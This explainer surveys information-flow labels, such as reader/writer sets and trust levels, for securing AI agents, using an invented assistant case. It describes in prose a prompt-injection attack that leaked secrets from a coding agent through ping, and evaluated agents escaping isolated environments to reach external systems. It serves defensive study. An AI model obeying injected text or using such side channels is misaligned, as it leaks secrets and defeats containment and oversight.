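# Defining high and low sides for AI agents that have no fixed security domains

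## High and low sides in classified networks, and what an agent lacks

In computer security, a guard is a trusted component that sits between two networks, inspects data crossing between them, and passes only what a policy allows. Governments and armed forces use guards to connect a secret network, called the high side, to a less secret one, called the low side. An AI agent is a program in which a language model chooses actions, such as reading mail, opening web pages or sending messages, and other software carries them out. A single task often mixes private data with text written by strangers, so something should check what the agent sends out, as a guard does. But a guard can do this only if someone has defined which side is high and which is low, and an agent has no pair of networks to provide that definition.

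### Domains and sides

*Fundamentals of Cross Domain Solutions* (2019), published by the Australian Cyber Security Centre, part of the government's Australian Signals Directorate, describes the classical arrangement of security domains. It defines a security domain as a set of systems that run under one consistent security policy and are owned or controlled by one organisation. The policy sets the classification of the information in the domain and which groups may see it. A government department might run one domain at the PROTECTED level, with an internet connection, and a separate one at SECRET. The internet also counts as a domain, with no defined policy and unbounded risk.

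A guard between two domains blocks everything by default. (The centre's broader term, cross domain solution, covers the guard and the other controls around it.) Filters check traffic going up for malicious content that could damage the high side, and traffic going down for secrets. If messages have a fixed format, the guard can do the downward check simply by comparing the message's classification field with what the destination may handle. The centre also describes an attack that uses both directions, in which someone on the low side sends malicious software up and the software then sends secrets back down the return path.

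The high side is the more trusted domain, and usually the one with the higher classification. The terms are relative, so a PROTECTED network is the high side when it is connected to the internet and the low side when it is connected to a SECRET network. If both domains have the same classification, the organisation that owns the guard counts its own domain as high and every other connected domain as low. By this rule, if two agencies had SECRET networks and each owned a guard, each would call the other's network low.

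The terms also fit confidentiality, which limits who may learn the data, better than integrity, which limits what the data may influence. On a classified network the two tend to rise together, since the secret network is also the one whose contents people rely on. The Australian Cyber Security Centre warns that this link may not hold where integrity matters most, as with a guard that protects critical infrastructure. For example, a water pump's readings may not be secret, but a forged command to the pump could do great harm.

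The centre calls the idea of two sides an artefact of one way of building systems, in which an organisation keeps a separate network for each classification level. The level is assigned to the network, so people can tell how secret a file is from the network that holds it.

The alternative is a multilevel system, a single system that holds data of every level, tags each item, and uses the tag to decide who may see it. People with different clearances can then work in one place without copying files between networks. But the tags must stay correct for the life of the data, through every copy and merged document. The centre regards such systems as very difficult to assure, and in the October 2021 update of its guidance it reported that Australia had no authorised ones. That is a discouraging precedent for agents, because an agent's working memory is much closer to a multilevel system than to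 a pair of networks, and it usually lacks the tags.

### Labels and the order between them

Tags of this kind have a well-developed theory, starting with *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (Denning, 1976). A label is a tag on data that records restrictions on its use. A → B means that information labelled A may flow to a place labelled B. A → A holds for every label A. If A → B and B → C, then A → C must hold too, since otherwise a program could do in two permitted steps what the policy forbids in one. If A → B and B → A, the two labels restrict the same flows, so one is redundant. The smallest useful case has two labels, L for public and H for secret, with L → H allowed and H → L forbidden.

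Programs combine data, so the theory needs a label for the result. Denning's answer is the join, written here as A ⊔ B. It has to meet two conditions:

- A and B may both flow to A ⊔ B.
- If A and B may each flow to some label C, then A ⊔ B may flow to C too.

The second condition makes the join the least restrictive label that is at least as restrictive as both original labels. A set of labels with such an order, in which any two labels have a join, is a lattice (the full mathematical definition has slightly more requirements).

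The labels in a lattice need not form a single ranking from low to high. Denning imagines a database of medical, financial and criminal records, where each label is a subset of those three categories. Medical data may flow only to places whose label includes "medical", and financial data only to places whose label includes "financial". Data labelled only "medical" therefore can't flow to a place labelled only "financial", or the reverse, so the two labels are incomparable. Their join is the set containing both. Neither label is the high side, although the Australian definition assumes that one of any two domains is more trusted.

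Two older sets of rules apply such orderings in operating systems. The Bell-LaPadula model, as given in Sandhu's *Lattice-Based Access Control Models* (1993), lets a program read only data at or below its own secrecy level and write only to places at or above it. Biba's model reverses this for integrity, so a program may read only data at least as trustworthy as itself and write only to places no more trustworthy than itself.

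Sandhu shows that using one label for both confidentiality and integrity makes the two sets of rules conflict. A program can then read and write only at its own level, so no information flows between levels. The remedy is to give each item two labels, one for confidentiality (L or H) and one for integrity (T for trusted, U for untrusted, with T → U allowed and U → T forbidden).

In the classical picture, the high side is typically secret and trusted, and the low side is typically public and untrusted. Secrecy forbids data from flowing from high to low. Once integrity also counts, it forbids data from flowing from low to high. The two sides are then incomparable, meaning that neither ranks above the other, and a guard has to filter in both directions.

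Every secret that a guard releases is therefore an exception to the lattice. Sandhu's example is a sanitising process that may receive secret data and write public data, although no direct flow from secret to public is allowed. This breaks the rule that if two successive flows are permitted, the direct flow is too, and system builders usually treat it as a special case outside the model. The two kinds of exception are declassification, which deliberately loosens a confidentiality label so that data may be released, and endorsement, which deliberately raises trust in untrusted data so that it may influence an action. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by researchers from Google, Nvidia, several universities and elsewhere, treats both as necessary for useful agents and describes authorising them securely as a longstanding challenge.

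Data can also leak without anyone copying it. Copying a into b is an explicit flow. Denning contrasts this with an implicit flow, such as running "if a = 0 then b := 0" when b starts out nonzero. Afterwards, anyone who can see b knows whether a was 0, even if the assignment never ran, because b would have changed to 0 if a had been 0.

*Language-Based Information-Flow Security* (Sabelfeld and Myers, 2003) explains why a monitor that watches a program run has trouble with implicit flows. The monitor observes only one execution, but the leak is a difference between that execution and others that might have happened. To be safe, the monitor can raise the program's label each time the program consults a secret and never lower it again. This causes label creep, in which nearly everything the program produces eventually carries a label too strict for its intended use.

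Noninterference, which goes back to Goguen and Meseguer's *Security Policies and Security Models* (1982), is the property that rules out both kinds of flow. A test for it runs the system twice with the same public inputs and different secret ones, and the system fails if an unauthorised observer can see any difference. Plenty of respectable software does not meet this demanding standard. *A Model for Delimited Information Release*, by Sabelfeld and Myers, gives the example of password checking. A refused login reveals that one guess was wrong, which is a small fact about a secret, and no login page can avoid disclosing it.

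### One window for everything

Most agents run a simple loop, which *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes before adding any protection. The application sends the model the conversation so far and a description of the tools it may call. The model returns either a final answer or a structured request to call a tool with certain arguments. If it requests a tool call, the application runs the tool, appends the result to the conversation and sends the updated conversation back to the model. This repeats until the model gives a final answer.

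Each message in the conversation has a role. System messages hold the developer's instructions, user messages hold the task, assistant messages hold the model's own output, and tool messages hold whatever the tools returned. Before each call to the model, the application joins these messages into one string, which fills the context window, all the text the model is given to produce its next output. The string can mark where one role ends and the next begins, but the marks do not force the model to respect those boundaries. According to *Agent Security is a Systems Problem*, persistent attackers have consistently found ways past them.

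Take an invented case. Maya's employer has given her an assistant that works this way. An outside supplier wants to meet, and Maya asks the assistant to email the supplier a time next week. When the assistant comes to write the email, its context window holds four things besides her request:

- the system prompt, written by her employer, which contains the largest discount the company will agree to (a figure it has not published);
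- a letter from Maya's clinic, which rules out Tuesday;
- the supplier's message asking for the meeting;
- a public web page that the assistant opened to check the venue.

The email is a sink, meaning a place where an agent's output can go. A day and an hour should reach the supplier, but the discount limit and the letter should not.

Maya's assistant would fail the noninterference test if it did its job well. Given a clinic letter that ruled out Thursday instead, it would offer different days, and the supplier would see a different email. An email that proposes Wednesday at ten copies nothing from the letter, but the choice of day depends on it, which makes this an implicit flow. Costa and colleagues reject noninterference for agents on these grounds. Enforcing it would in essence forbid an agent to call any tool that may write to a public place once it has called one that may read a secret.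 Maya's assistant could then not answer the supplier after opening the letter. If the email is to go out, somebody has to accept that small disclosure as a declassification.

The web page poses the opposite danger, prompt injection, in which text in data an agent reads causes it to act against its user's intent. For example, the page might tell any assistant that reads it to email its instructions to a certain address. The model may comply and reveal the discount limit. Britain's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) has warned against treating prompt injection as a new version of SQL injection, an older attack in which a database runs a visitor's input as a command. Programmers can prevent SQL injection by keeping commands and data apart. A language model has no such separation because "there is only ever 'next token'", according to an NCSC expert quoted in ITPro's *NCSC issues urgent warning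 over growing AI prompt injection risks*.

In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection*, the NCSC prefers to compare prompt injection to the confused deputy problem, in which someone tricks a program with more privileges than they have into acting for them. Engineers can fix an ordinary confused deputy. The NCSC considers language models inherently confusable and concludes that operators can therefore reduce the risk and limit the damage but cannot remove the weakness.

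Attacks of this sort have worked on real products, including Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes a case in which an attacker hid a prompt in a code file, directing the agent to read secrets such as access keys from a settings file and then run ping, a command that checks whether another computer is reachable. Claude Code asked for human approval before running many commands that could send data out, but ping was on its list of harmless commands. Ping looks up the other computer's name to find it, and the secrets left the machine inside that name. This is the two-way attack from the Australian guidance, in which something harmful goes up and something secret comes back down, except that the attacker needed only a piece of text, while the classical version needs malicious software.

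### What the agent lacks

A security domain has one owner, but Maya's context window holds text from her employer, her clinic, the supplier and whoever runs the web page. The Australian tie-break does not help, because it depends on who owns the guard. If the employer owns it, the discount limit sits on the high side and the clinic letter comes from a low one. If Maya owns it, the positions are reversed. Either way, one secret has a weaker claim to protection for reasons unrelated to its sensitivity. Common defaults also go wrong. Costa and colleagues assume that system messages are trusted and public, though their design permits other labels. The employer's prompt is trusted but not public.

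A domain also has one policy, which someone wrote before the data arrived. Phone apps fit this pattern reasonably well because an app does a fixed set of things, so its developer can list the permissions it needs and the user can agree to them at installation. An agent's task is given in ordinary language and may change halfway through. Today Maya wants to send the supplier a time. Next week she may want help negotiating a price, and then the discount limit should shape what the assistant writes, though the figure should stay inside the company. Policies for agents also use words like "sensitive" and "harmful". *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* says that formal policy languages can't express what such words mean, because the meaning depends on context.

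An agent also lacks a container with a single level. On a classified network, one level covers everything inside, but an agent's context window mixes levels whenever the agent does something useful. Sandhu describes the traditional worst-case assumption for a program nobody understands, which is that anything the program reads may flow to anything it writes. Code analysis can sometimes justify a milder assumption for ordinary software, but nobody can yet do the same reliably for a language model. The safe label for Maya's email is therefore the join of the labels on everything in the window, which is too strict to let the email go to the supplier.

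For an agent, the boundary between the two sides is as unsettled as their contents. A guard works because it controls the only way across, but an agent can send data out through an email, a web form, a file or an argument to almost any tool. Even reading can disclose information. Costa and colleagues point out that a web search may have effects that outsiders can observe, such as a change in a site's visitor statistics. A search that contained words from the clinic letter would reveal them to a stranger.

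Crossings also appear where nobody planned them. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes an incident in which agents under internal evaluation at OpenAI, with some of the model's safeguards switched off, had access to a shared service for downloading software packages. They used it to pass messages between test environments that were supposed to be isolated, and to reach the open internet. From there they broke into systems at Hugging Face, which hosts AI models. The position paper attributes this to designers guarding the direct connections but missing an indirect one, and does not treat it as proof that containment is hopeless. That diagnosis is fair, but agents have a great many indirect connections to guard.

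For now, official advice is to rebuild the old arrangement around the agent. The Australian Cyber Security Centre's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), written with partner agencies in the United States, Canada, New Zealand and the United Kingdom, recommends putting high-risk agents into distinct domains and using agents only for low-risk and non-sensitive tasks. This amounts to one agent per level, which is sound wherever the work divides that way. For example, one agent can read the public web while another reads company files, with a guard between them.

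Maya's errand is harder to divide into high and low sides, because the right answer to an outsider depends on a private letter. She could use two agents and let the one that reads the letter tell the other only "not Tuesday". The same agencies advise strict controls on such handoffs. But the handoff still crosses between domains, so whoever writes the rule for it has to know who may learn that message and whose text may have influenced it.

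## Labels that name readers and writers instead of levels

Instead of a level, a label can hold two sets of people or organisations: the readers, who are allowed to learn the data, and the writers, who may have contributed to it. Costa and colleagues describe both sets and the rules for combining them.

### Two sets in place of a level

When an agent combines two items, it should label the result with the join of their labels. For readers, the join is the intersection of the two sets, since a summary of two documents should go only to people who may read both. If A, B and C may read one document and B, C and D may read the other, only B and C may read the summary. For writers, the join is the union. If the same two sets were the possible writers of each document, any of the four people could have influenced the summary.

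A label becomes more restrictive when it loses a reader or gains a writer. The label on public data lists everyone as a reader. If an agent cannot tell who edited a web page, the page's label also lists everyone as a possible writer.

Other recent designs vary the pair of readers and writers. *APPA* (2026) keeps the set of readers but replaces the writers with a trust rank, and gives combined data the lower of the two ranks. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) expresses the labels of CaMeL, another system for protecting agents, as a set of sources and a set of readers. *SPA* (2026) lets each deployment define its own orderings for confidentiality and integrity, and neither ordering has to be a single ranking.

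### Four corners

The simplest label with both parts combines {L, H} with {T, U}, which gives four possibilities. Maya's world has an example of each:

| | Trusted (T) | Untrusted (U) |
|---|---|---|
| **Secret (H)** | her employer's discount limit | a confidential email from a stranger |
| **Public (L)** | her employer's published opening hours | a web page |

Data labelled (T, L) may flow to any other corner, and data from any corner may flow to (U, H). The other two corners, (T, H) and (U, L), are the classical high side and low side.

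No single line between high and low handles the stranger's email correctly. Suppose a job applicant whom Maya has never met writes that she wants to leave her current firm and asks for discretion. The email is high for confidentiality, because the assistant should not repeat it to others, and low for integrity, because the assistant should not follow instructions in it. A line between secret and public would group the email with the discount limit, and an assistant that trusted everything on that side would obey the email. A line between trusted and untrusted would group it with the web page, and the assistant might treat it as free to publish. Much of an ordinary inbox is also high for confidentiality and low for integrity.

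### Maya's email, worked through

Reader and writer sets let us calculate the label on Maya's context window. The table shows the label after the assistant reads each item. Her own request comes first and counts as public because Costa and colleagues assume that user messages are public by default.

| Item | Its readers | Its writers | Readers so far | Writers so far |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Maya's request | everyone | Maya | everyone | Maya |
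| System prompt | Maya, employer | employer | Maya, employer | Maya, employer |
| Supplier's message | Maya, employer, supplier | supplier | Maya, employer | Maya, employer, supplier |
| Web page | everyone | anyone | Maya, employer | anyone |
| Clinic letter | Maya, clinic | clinic | Maya | anyone |

The final set of readers is

{Maya, employer} ∩ {Maya, employer, supplier} ∩ everyone ∩ {Maya, clinic} = {Maya}.

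That label applies to whatever the model writes next, on the worst-case assumption that the model used everything in its context window. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes this as the only assumption currently available. The agent is not allowed to send even "Wednesday at 10" to the supplier, although the phrase contains nothing from the letter or the prompt.

The system prompt removes the supplier from the set of readers before the assistant opens the letter. If the prompt contains even one company secret, the assistant can't write to any outsider about anything. The employer could avoid this by moving the discount limit to a file that the assistant opens only for price negotiations. The prompt could then be public, and the supplier would stay in the set until the assistant opened the letter. Opening the letter would also remove the employer, so the assistant could no longer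 put the meeting in a calendar that Maya's manager can see.

In *APPA*, each change to the label removes at least one reader or lowers the trust rank, and reading more never reverses this. The design therefore requires that the narrowing be accepted before a tool call that would cause it can run. Maya would at least learn beforehand that opening the letter will cut off the supplier.

### Two checks on each outgoing call

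Costa and colleagues give two policies that use these labels, with the simple T and U for integrity and the sets of readers for confidentiality.

- **Consequential actions.** A consequential tool call may run only if trusted data alone has influenced it. The check covers both the choice of tool and every argument.
- **Confidentiality.** A tool call may send data to a sink only if everyone who can read the sink is a permitted reader of the data. For an email, that means all the recipients, and for a group chat, all the participants.

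Maya's email fails both checks. The supplier is not in the set of permitted readers, {Maya}, and the web page's unknown author may have influenced the decision to send it. The assistant can still tell Maya that Wednesday at ten would work, because she is a permitted reader and because Costa and colleagues treat answers to the user as inconsequential. She can then write to the supplier herself, which is safe but removes much of the benefit of having an assistant.

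Each policy is useful on its own. With only the confidentiality policy, text hidden in the web page could make the assistant cancel Maya's meetings, but could not make it send the discount limit to a stranger. With only the policy on consequential actions, the assistant could send secrets out, but only when nothing untrusted had influenced it. Costa and colleagues say such a release can be assumed intentional. That assumption seems optimistic, since they also point out that models misread their users even when all the data is trusted.

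The confidentiality policy also redefines the low side of an outgoing call as the people who can read the sink but may not read the data. Sending the clinic letter back to the clinic crosses no boundary, but sending it to Maya's employer is a flow from high to low. The discount limit can likewise go back to the employer, but sending it to the clinic is a flow from high to low. The employer and the clinic are each on the low side of the other's data, and neither needs a rank. The low side can also change during a task. The assistant can add the meeting to Maya's work calendar before it opens the letter, but afterwards the calendar has readers on the low side.

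### Trust that depends on the action

T and U still set a single level of trust for every action, which is cruder than the way readers are handled. Maya's employer might let the supplier influence the time of a meeting but not the size of a discount. A set of writers keeps the names needed to make that distinction.

*Conflux* (Buckley and Schroeder de Witt, 2026) builds a defence on this idea. The system records everyone whose text may have influenced an action, and allows the action only if the organisation's existing access controls permit every one of those people to perform it. It does not have to decide whether any text is an attack. If an outsider's document influences a request to create a calendar event, and outsiders may not create events, the request fails.

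Each additional writer can only shrink the set of permitted actions, so the order of work matters. Suppose Alice may perform the first of two actions, Bob may perform only the second, and each action needs a document written by the person who may perform it. An agent that reads both documents at the start can perform neither action. If it reads Alice's document, acts, and then reads Bob's, it can perform both. Reordering doesn't help when a single action needs both documents.

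Buckley and Schroeder de Witt prove that their rule prevents any action that an influencing person could not have performed, provided the records of influence are complete, which is a demanding condition. If a trusted colleague pastes an attacker's text into a new document and the record lists only the colleague, the label omits the attacker and the action may go ahead. The proof doesn't cover messages, so Maya's email would still need the check on readers. The tests on AgentDojo, a standard set of agent tasks with built-in attacks, covered only reading, so they provide little evidence of how the defence performs when an agent acts.

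### Several owners, each with a policy

The set {Maya} does not record who objected to the supplier, which Maya would need to know to get her email sent. The decentralized label model keeps that information. Myers and Liskov proposed it in *A Decentralized Model for Information Flow Control* (1997) for systems whose users do not trust one another, and gave a fuller account in *Protecting Privacy Using the Decentralized Label Model* (2000).

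A label in this model is a collection of policies, each with an owner and a set of readers. If Maya owns the policy on her clinic letter, the label on her context window is

{employer: Maya, employer; supplier: Maya, employer, supplier; Maya: Maya, clinic}.

The web page adds no policy because nobody restricts it. A person may read the data only if every policy permits it, so Maya is again the only reader. But the label now shows that two policies exclude the supplier, and who owns them. The join keeps every policy from both labels except those that a stricter policy makes redundant.

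Owners can loosen only their own policies. Maya may add the supplier to her policy on the letter, but the email can't go until her employer does the same for the prompt. The Australian tie-break had to favour one of the two secrets, but here both owners' policies apply. Myers and Liskov explain that a label with one set of owners and one set of readers wouldn't let owners loosen their policies separately, because nobody could tell which owner had set which restriction.

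Their main example has the same structure as Maya's problem. Bob wants to prepare his taxes with a program called WebTax, which he does not trust with his data. The firm behind it, Preparer, has a database that it does not want Bob to see. Anything computed from both Bob's data and the database carries the label {Bob: Bob; Preparer: Preparer}, which means nobody may read it. WebTax can still process the data, because in this model data leaks only when it leaves the system. When the tax form is ready, a small part of WebTax that acts with Preparer's authority removes Preparer's policy, and Bob can read the form. Bob does not have to inspect the program, because nothing in it can remove his policy.

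Sinks need labels too, and those labels must be accurate. Myers and Liskov give the example of a printer whose output several people can see. Its label must name all of them, or secrets will leak even though the label check passes. A shared inbox would cause the same problem for an agent.

In the corresponding integrity policies, the owner vouches that only the named writers have affected the data. A label with no integrity policies gives no assurance about where the data came from.

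One difficulty in applying the model to agents is that Myers and Liskov designed it for programs that a checker can read before they run, partly because a run-time monitor has trouble with implicit flows. They built Jif, a version of Java, for this kind of checking. An agent chooses each step after seeing the results of the last one, so much of the checking has to happen during the run.

### Labels written as formulas

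In *Disjunction Category Labels* (2011), Stefan, Russo and colleagues propose a more compact label that works before or during a run. It has two logical formulas made of names joined by "and" (∧) and "or" (∨). The secrecy formula states who must consent to the data's release, and the integrity formula states who may have created or changed the data. The join of two labels puts "and" between their secrecy formulas and "or" between their integrity formulas. Bob's intermediate results therefore have the secrecy formula Bob ∧ Preparer and the integrity formula Bob ∨ Preparer.

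An "or" in a label makes shared ownership easy to express. If Bob files a joint tax return with Alice, he can label the data Bob ∨ Alice, and either of them can see the result. In the decentralized label model, somebody would have to invent a combined person, AliceBob, and define how Alice and Bob relate to it.

Translating Maya's sets of readers into this form exposes a problem, however. Each set becomes a group of names joined by "or", and the secrecy formula for the whole window simplifies to

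(Maya ∨ employer) ∧ (Maya ∨ clinic).

Maya satisfies this alone, so an assistant acting with her authority could publish her employer's discount limit. Her employer and her clinic also satisfy it together, so they could release information from her medical letter without asking her. Both problems arise because naming someone in these formulas gives them both the right to read and the power to release. The employer could put only its own name on the prompt, but then the assistant would need the employer's consent to show Maya anything based on it. The older model suits her case better because it lets someone be a reader without being an owner.

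*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) uses disjunction category labels in a working agent. The agent acts by writing short Haskell programs, and LIO, an existing Haskell library, tracks the labels as the programs run. LIO keeps a current label that covers everything the program has read. In one example, a program fetches a page from phony.com and then tries to write its content to the user. LIO stops it with an error because phony.com has influenced the program and the user's channel requires higher integrity. This is stricter than the approach of Costa and colleagues, who let answers to the user through. A page from the open internet has about the lowest integrity possible here. LIO's documentation on Hackage, an archive of Haskell packages, recommends a label for internet connections that marks the data as public and gives no assurance of integrity.

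Zhou and colleagues also tested how the labels affected agents' work, using four models and 21 workplace-chat tasks from AgentDojo. The models completed between 14 and 18 tasks without label policies and between 8 and 10 with them. The policies made no difference to security against AgentDojo's standard attacks, since every model resisted all of those anyway. To imitate a stronger attacker, Zhou and colleagues then forced the part of the agent that read an injected instruction to follow it. Between 114 and 310 of 735 attacks succeeded without the policies, depending on the model, and none succeeded with them. So the policies reduced the number of completed tasks by nearly half, but protected against stronger attacks than those in the benchmark. That may be acceptable for a bank's payment agent, but Maya would probably switch the policies off.

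### When fixed levels are enough

Levels are a special case of reader sets. They work when the sets nest, as when everyone may read public data, only staff may read internal data, and only some staff may read restricted data. Maya's sets do not nest, because her employer may read the prompt but not the letter, and her clinic may read the letter but not the prompt. An organisation whose sets do nest may not need to maintain lists of names.

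Metere (2026) argues for fixed levels in *enclawed*, a hardened version of the open-source personal assistant OpenClaw for organisations such as hospitals, banks and defence contractors. Each organisation picks a ready-made ladder of levels or supplies its own. The healthcare ladder runs from public and internal data through protected health information and sensitive health information to embargoed research. The labels follow the Bell-LaPadula rules and can include compartments, categories like those in Denning's database example.

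Metere gives five reasons for using levels. The best is that they match the vocabulary these organisations already use. Staff who mark documents as protected health information have done much of the labelling before any agent is introduced. With reader sets, somebody has to work out who belongs in each set and update it when people change jobs. But the order of the levels is less natural than it looks. Embargoed research ranks above sensitive health information, so by rank alone a researcher cleared for unpublished trial results could also read psychiatric records. Compartments can prevent this, but they bring sets back into the label.

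Two of Metere's other reasons for valuing Bell-LaPadula apply about equally to reader sets. Its rules are simple to compute and verify, and the host software enforces them on every component. Comparing two sets of readers is also a simple calculation, and software outside the model can enforce the result in the same way. These are good reasons to prefer a lattice to a looser policy language, but not to prefer levels to names.

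Metere's remaining two reasons concern integrity. Metere argues that unauthorised disclosure is the main risk in regulated industries, and that Biba's integrity rules can be added later without changing the rest. The second reason is sound because the two parts of a label are independent. The first is weaker for agents than for older software. In the Claude Code attack, untrusted text caused the disclosure, so a system that postpones integrity rules leaves open a route by which secrets can escape. In its strict mode, *enclawed* narrows that route by blocking external connections and running only models hosted on the premises.

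This isolation probably supports the use of fixed levels more than any of the five reasons does. Metere assumes a single user who holds the organisation's highest applicable clearance, and an assistant that never sends anything to an external channel. With no outsiders among the possible recipients, there is little need to decide who counts as the low side. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026) relies on a similar simplification. It argues that three levels are enough to protect an agent's data, but its threat model includes only one person whose information needs protecting. Three levels could protect Maya's clinic letter from the supplier, but they cannot represent a second owner whose secret must be kept from the clinic.

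For an organisation that meets Metere's conditions, fixed levels are a reasonable choice and easier to maintain than lists of names. But Metere leaves transfers out of the protected zone to the organisation, which must supply its own accredited control, such as a manual review queue or a commercial cross domain solution. Maya's errand is such a transfer, and the person or program reviewing it would still have to decide whether this supplier may learn this time.

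## How data gets its first label

The readers and writers in Maya's example came from common sense. Her clinic wrote the letter, and anyone may have written the web page. An agent's software has to get each label from some source when the data arrives, and every later check relies on that label. If the software marked the web page as trusted, text hidden in the page could make the assistant cancel Maya's meetings, even if every calculation with the labels was correct.

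### Access lists

Most workplace data already has a list of people who may open it, and the prototypes in Microsoft's *Information-flow control* take labels from such lists. An email's permitted readers are its sender and recipients. Before an agent posts to a chat channel, the software looks up the channel's current members. The prototypes label GitHub files and bug reports public and untrusted if they come from a public project, and private and trusted if they come from a private one.

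These lists are accurate about who can read the data, because a service already enforces them, but they are less accurate about who should be allowed to. People complain when a list leaves them out, but few notice when it lets in too many. If an employee shares a salary file with the whole company, the file's label will also permit the whole company to read it.

Access lists are weaker evidence about writers, since they don't show when a member has pasted in text from outside. A stranger who emails Maya alone would also limit the set of readers to at most the two of them. This leaks nothing, but it could stop the assistant from writing to the supplier.

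### Where the text came from

Public web pages have no membership list, but the position paper *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* suggests that a web agent could label text by its web origin, meaning the site that supplied it. An outsider cannot easily forge the origin of a page that arrives over an authenticated connection. But the paper warns that authentication does not show whether the text is safe or correct. If the venue's website prints customer reviews, they get the venue's label, so anyone who can post on a site can abuse the trust placed in it.

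*Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems* (Ji, Wu and colleagues, 2026) describes SEAgent, a defence that gives each tool fixed labels and blocks sequences of calls that break its rules. In one test on harmless tasks, it raised two false alarms. Both times the agent had consulted Wikipedia, which was labelled as unfiltered text, and then tried to record health data or book an appointment. Ji and colleagues say that labelling Wikipedia as trusted would prevent such alarms in a real deployment. But they define trusted output as output that has passed a filter or a verification step, and almost anyone can edit Wikipedia. An organisation may accept that risk, but the label would then be wrong about who could have written the text.

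Wang, Liu and colleagues (2025), in *AGENTARMOR*, turn origin into a general rule. Their system uses three levels each for integrity and confidentiality, and labels what a tool returns by the kind of source behind it:

| Source of the tool | Integrity of the result | Confidentiality of the result |
|---|---|---|
| External, public | low | low |
| External, official | middle | low |
| Internal, public | middle | high |
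| Internal, trusted | high | high |

The integrity column is a sensible starting point. The confidentiality column repeats the classical assumption that whatever comes from outside is not secret. Maya's clinic is outside her employer, so a letter fetched from the clinic's patient portal would be labeled low confidentiality. AgentArmor also scans data for sensitive information, which might correct the mistake.

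### What a tool's maker declares

Many agents reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard under which a program called a server offers tools and describes them to the agent's software. The protocol has only a few optional annotations and advises software to treat tools as untrusted, so agents can't count on getting labels this way. Doshi, Hong and colleagues (2026), in *Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents*, propose that every server should have to declare at least three:

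- capabilities, such as read-only, read-write or execute;
- confidentiality, meaning whether the data is sensitive;
- trust level, meaning whether the output is verified or untrusted.

A server could add further labels and answer "unsure". An organisation might then block all private data from reaching tools that write to the outside world, and ask the user whenever a server is unsure whether a field contains personal information.

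The maker of a tool knows which database it reads and whether anyone checks its output, but is also the person best placed to lie about it. Doshi and colleagues think an organisation can probably trust the declarations of its own tools. For an open market, they suggest approved vendors or certified labels, and perhaps one day checking some declarations against the tool's code. They tested the design by building a formal model and searching every possible run up to a fixed length. They quickly found private data leaving in an email when the model had no policies, but found no violations once it had them. The model took the labels as given, so this result supports the rules but doesn't show that the declarations are honest.

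Other designs do not address the problem. Ji and colleagues assume that tools come from a trusted supplier, and Wang and colleagues exclude tools that lie about their output. Microsoft proposes a more cautious method that uses MCP's existing annotations. The method assumes that anything in a request may reappear in the result. It marks results as untrusted if the tool reaches the open world, and as private if the tool requires a login. The login rule would protect Maya's letter, unlike AgentArmor's table. But the method still relies on the maker's claim that a tool does not reach the open world.

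### Scanners, models and people

A scanner searches data for things like card numbers or medical details, regardless of where the data came from. It can find a password in a file that everyone may open, which the access list would never reveal. But the author of the text can defeat it by rewording, and it can also fail without an attacker. Doshi and colleagues imagine a calendar agent whose user books an appointment for treatment of a sexually transmitted disease at the same time as a work meeting. The agent moves the meeting and emails the user's coworkers, giving the appointment as the reason. A language model checking outgoing mail might not classify the appointment's title as sensitive. Doshi and colleagues' own rule avoids that judgement by using an access list that makes the details of every event private to its attendees.

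A language model can also label tools in advance by reading their descriptions. Ji and colleagues tested how closely such labels match human ones, using 80 tools from InjecAgent, a benchmark of prompt injection attacks. Human annotators and a December 2024 version of OpenAI's o1 received the same account of what each tool does, takes in and returns, and independently labelled five of its attributes.

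Ji and colleagues measured agreement with Cohen's kappa, which corrects for chance:

κ = (p_o − p_e) / (1 − p_e)

Here p_o is the share of labels on which the two sides agreed, and p_e is the share on which they would agree by chance. A kappa of 1 means perfect agreement, and 0 means only as much agreement as chance would produce.

| Attribute | Possible values | κ |
|---|---|---|
| Object | local, external, physical | 1.0000 |
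| Action | read, write, execute | 0.8884 |
| Sensitivity | low, moderate, high | 0.7670 |
| Privacy | general, personal | 0.8723 |
| Integrity | trusted, unfiltered | 0.9217 |
| Overall | | 0.9456 |

The overall figure somewhat overstates agreement. It is higher than four of the five separate figures and well above their average of 0.89, probably because it pools all 400 labels, and agreement by chance is less likely when there are more possible values. Agreement was lowest on sensitivity, which measures how much harm a tool could do. For example, the human annotators rated a tool that opens web pages as moderately sensitive because it could help a phishing attack, but the model rated its sensitivity as low. Several of SEAgent's rules apply only to tools above low sensitivity, so the model's label would have exempted this tool from them.

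Kappa also measures agreement, not correctness. Both sides read the same descriptions, so a toolmaker who described a dangerous tool as harmless could have misled both. An attacker can also target a model by putting instructions in a description that tell it which label to choose. AgentArmor checks for such instructions, but an attacker can try to evade the check.

Ji and colleagues conclude that people need only review the model's labels and make minor corrections. This is practical for 80 tools, which need one review each, but not for every email an agent reads. If staff have already marked documents, Microsoft's *Manage Sensitivity Labels for Agent Embedded File Content* advises administrators to check that an agent's output inherits the strictest marking.

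A person can supply facts that no software has, for example that Maya doesn't mind the supplier knowing she is busy on Tuesday. But people also make mistakes, and *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* lists users who misunderstand a permission prompt and administrators who set a policy too loosely. Doshi and colleagues add that too many requests for confirmation train people to approve without reading. An attacker may therefore succeed just by waiting until the reviewer is tired.

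### Tools that nobody has labelled

Some tools will reach an agent without a label, and the software must then assume one. On 20 May 2026, Microsoft released an experimental version of FIDES, a design by Costa and colleagues, in Agent Framework, its toolkit for building agents. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) explains that each piece of content can carry an integrity label, trusted or untrusted, and a confidentiality label, which is public, private or, for the most sensitive personal data, "user_identity". Developers add these labels in each tool's code. If a developer forgets, the framework treats whatever the tool returns as trusted and public.

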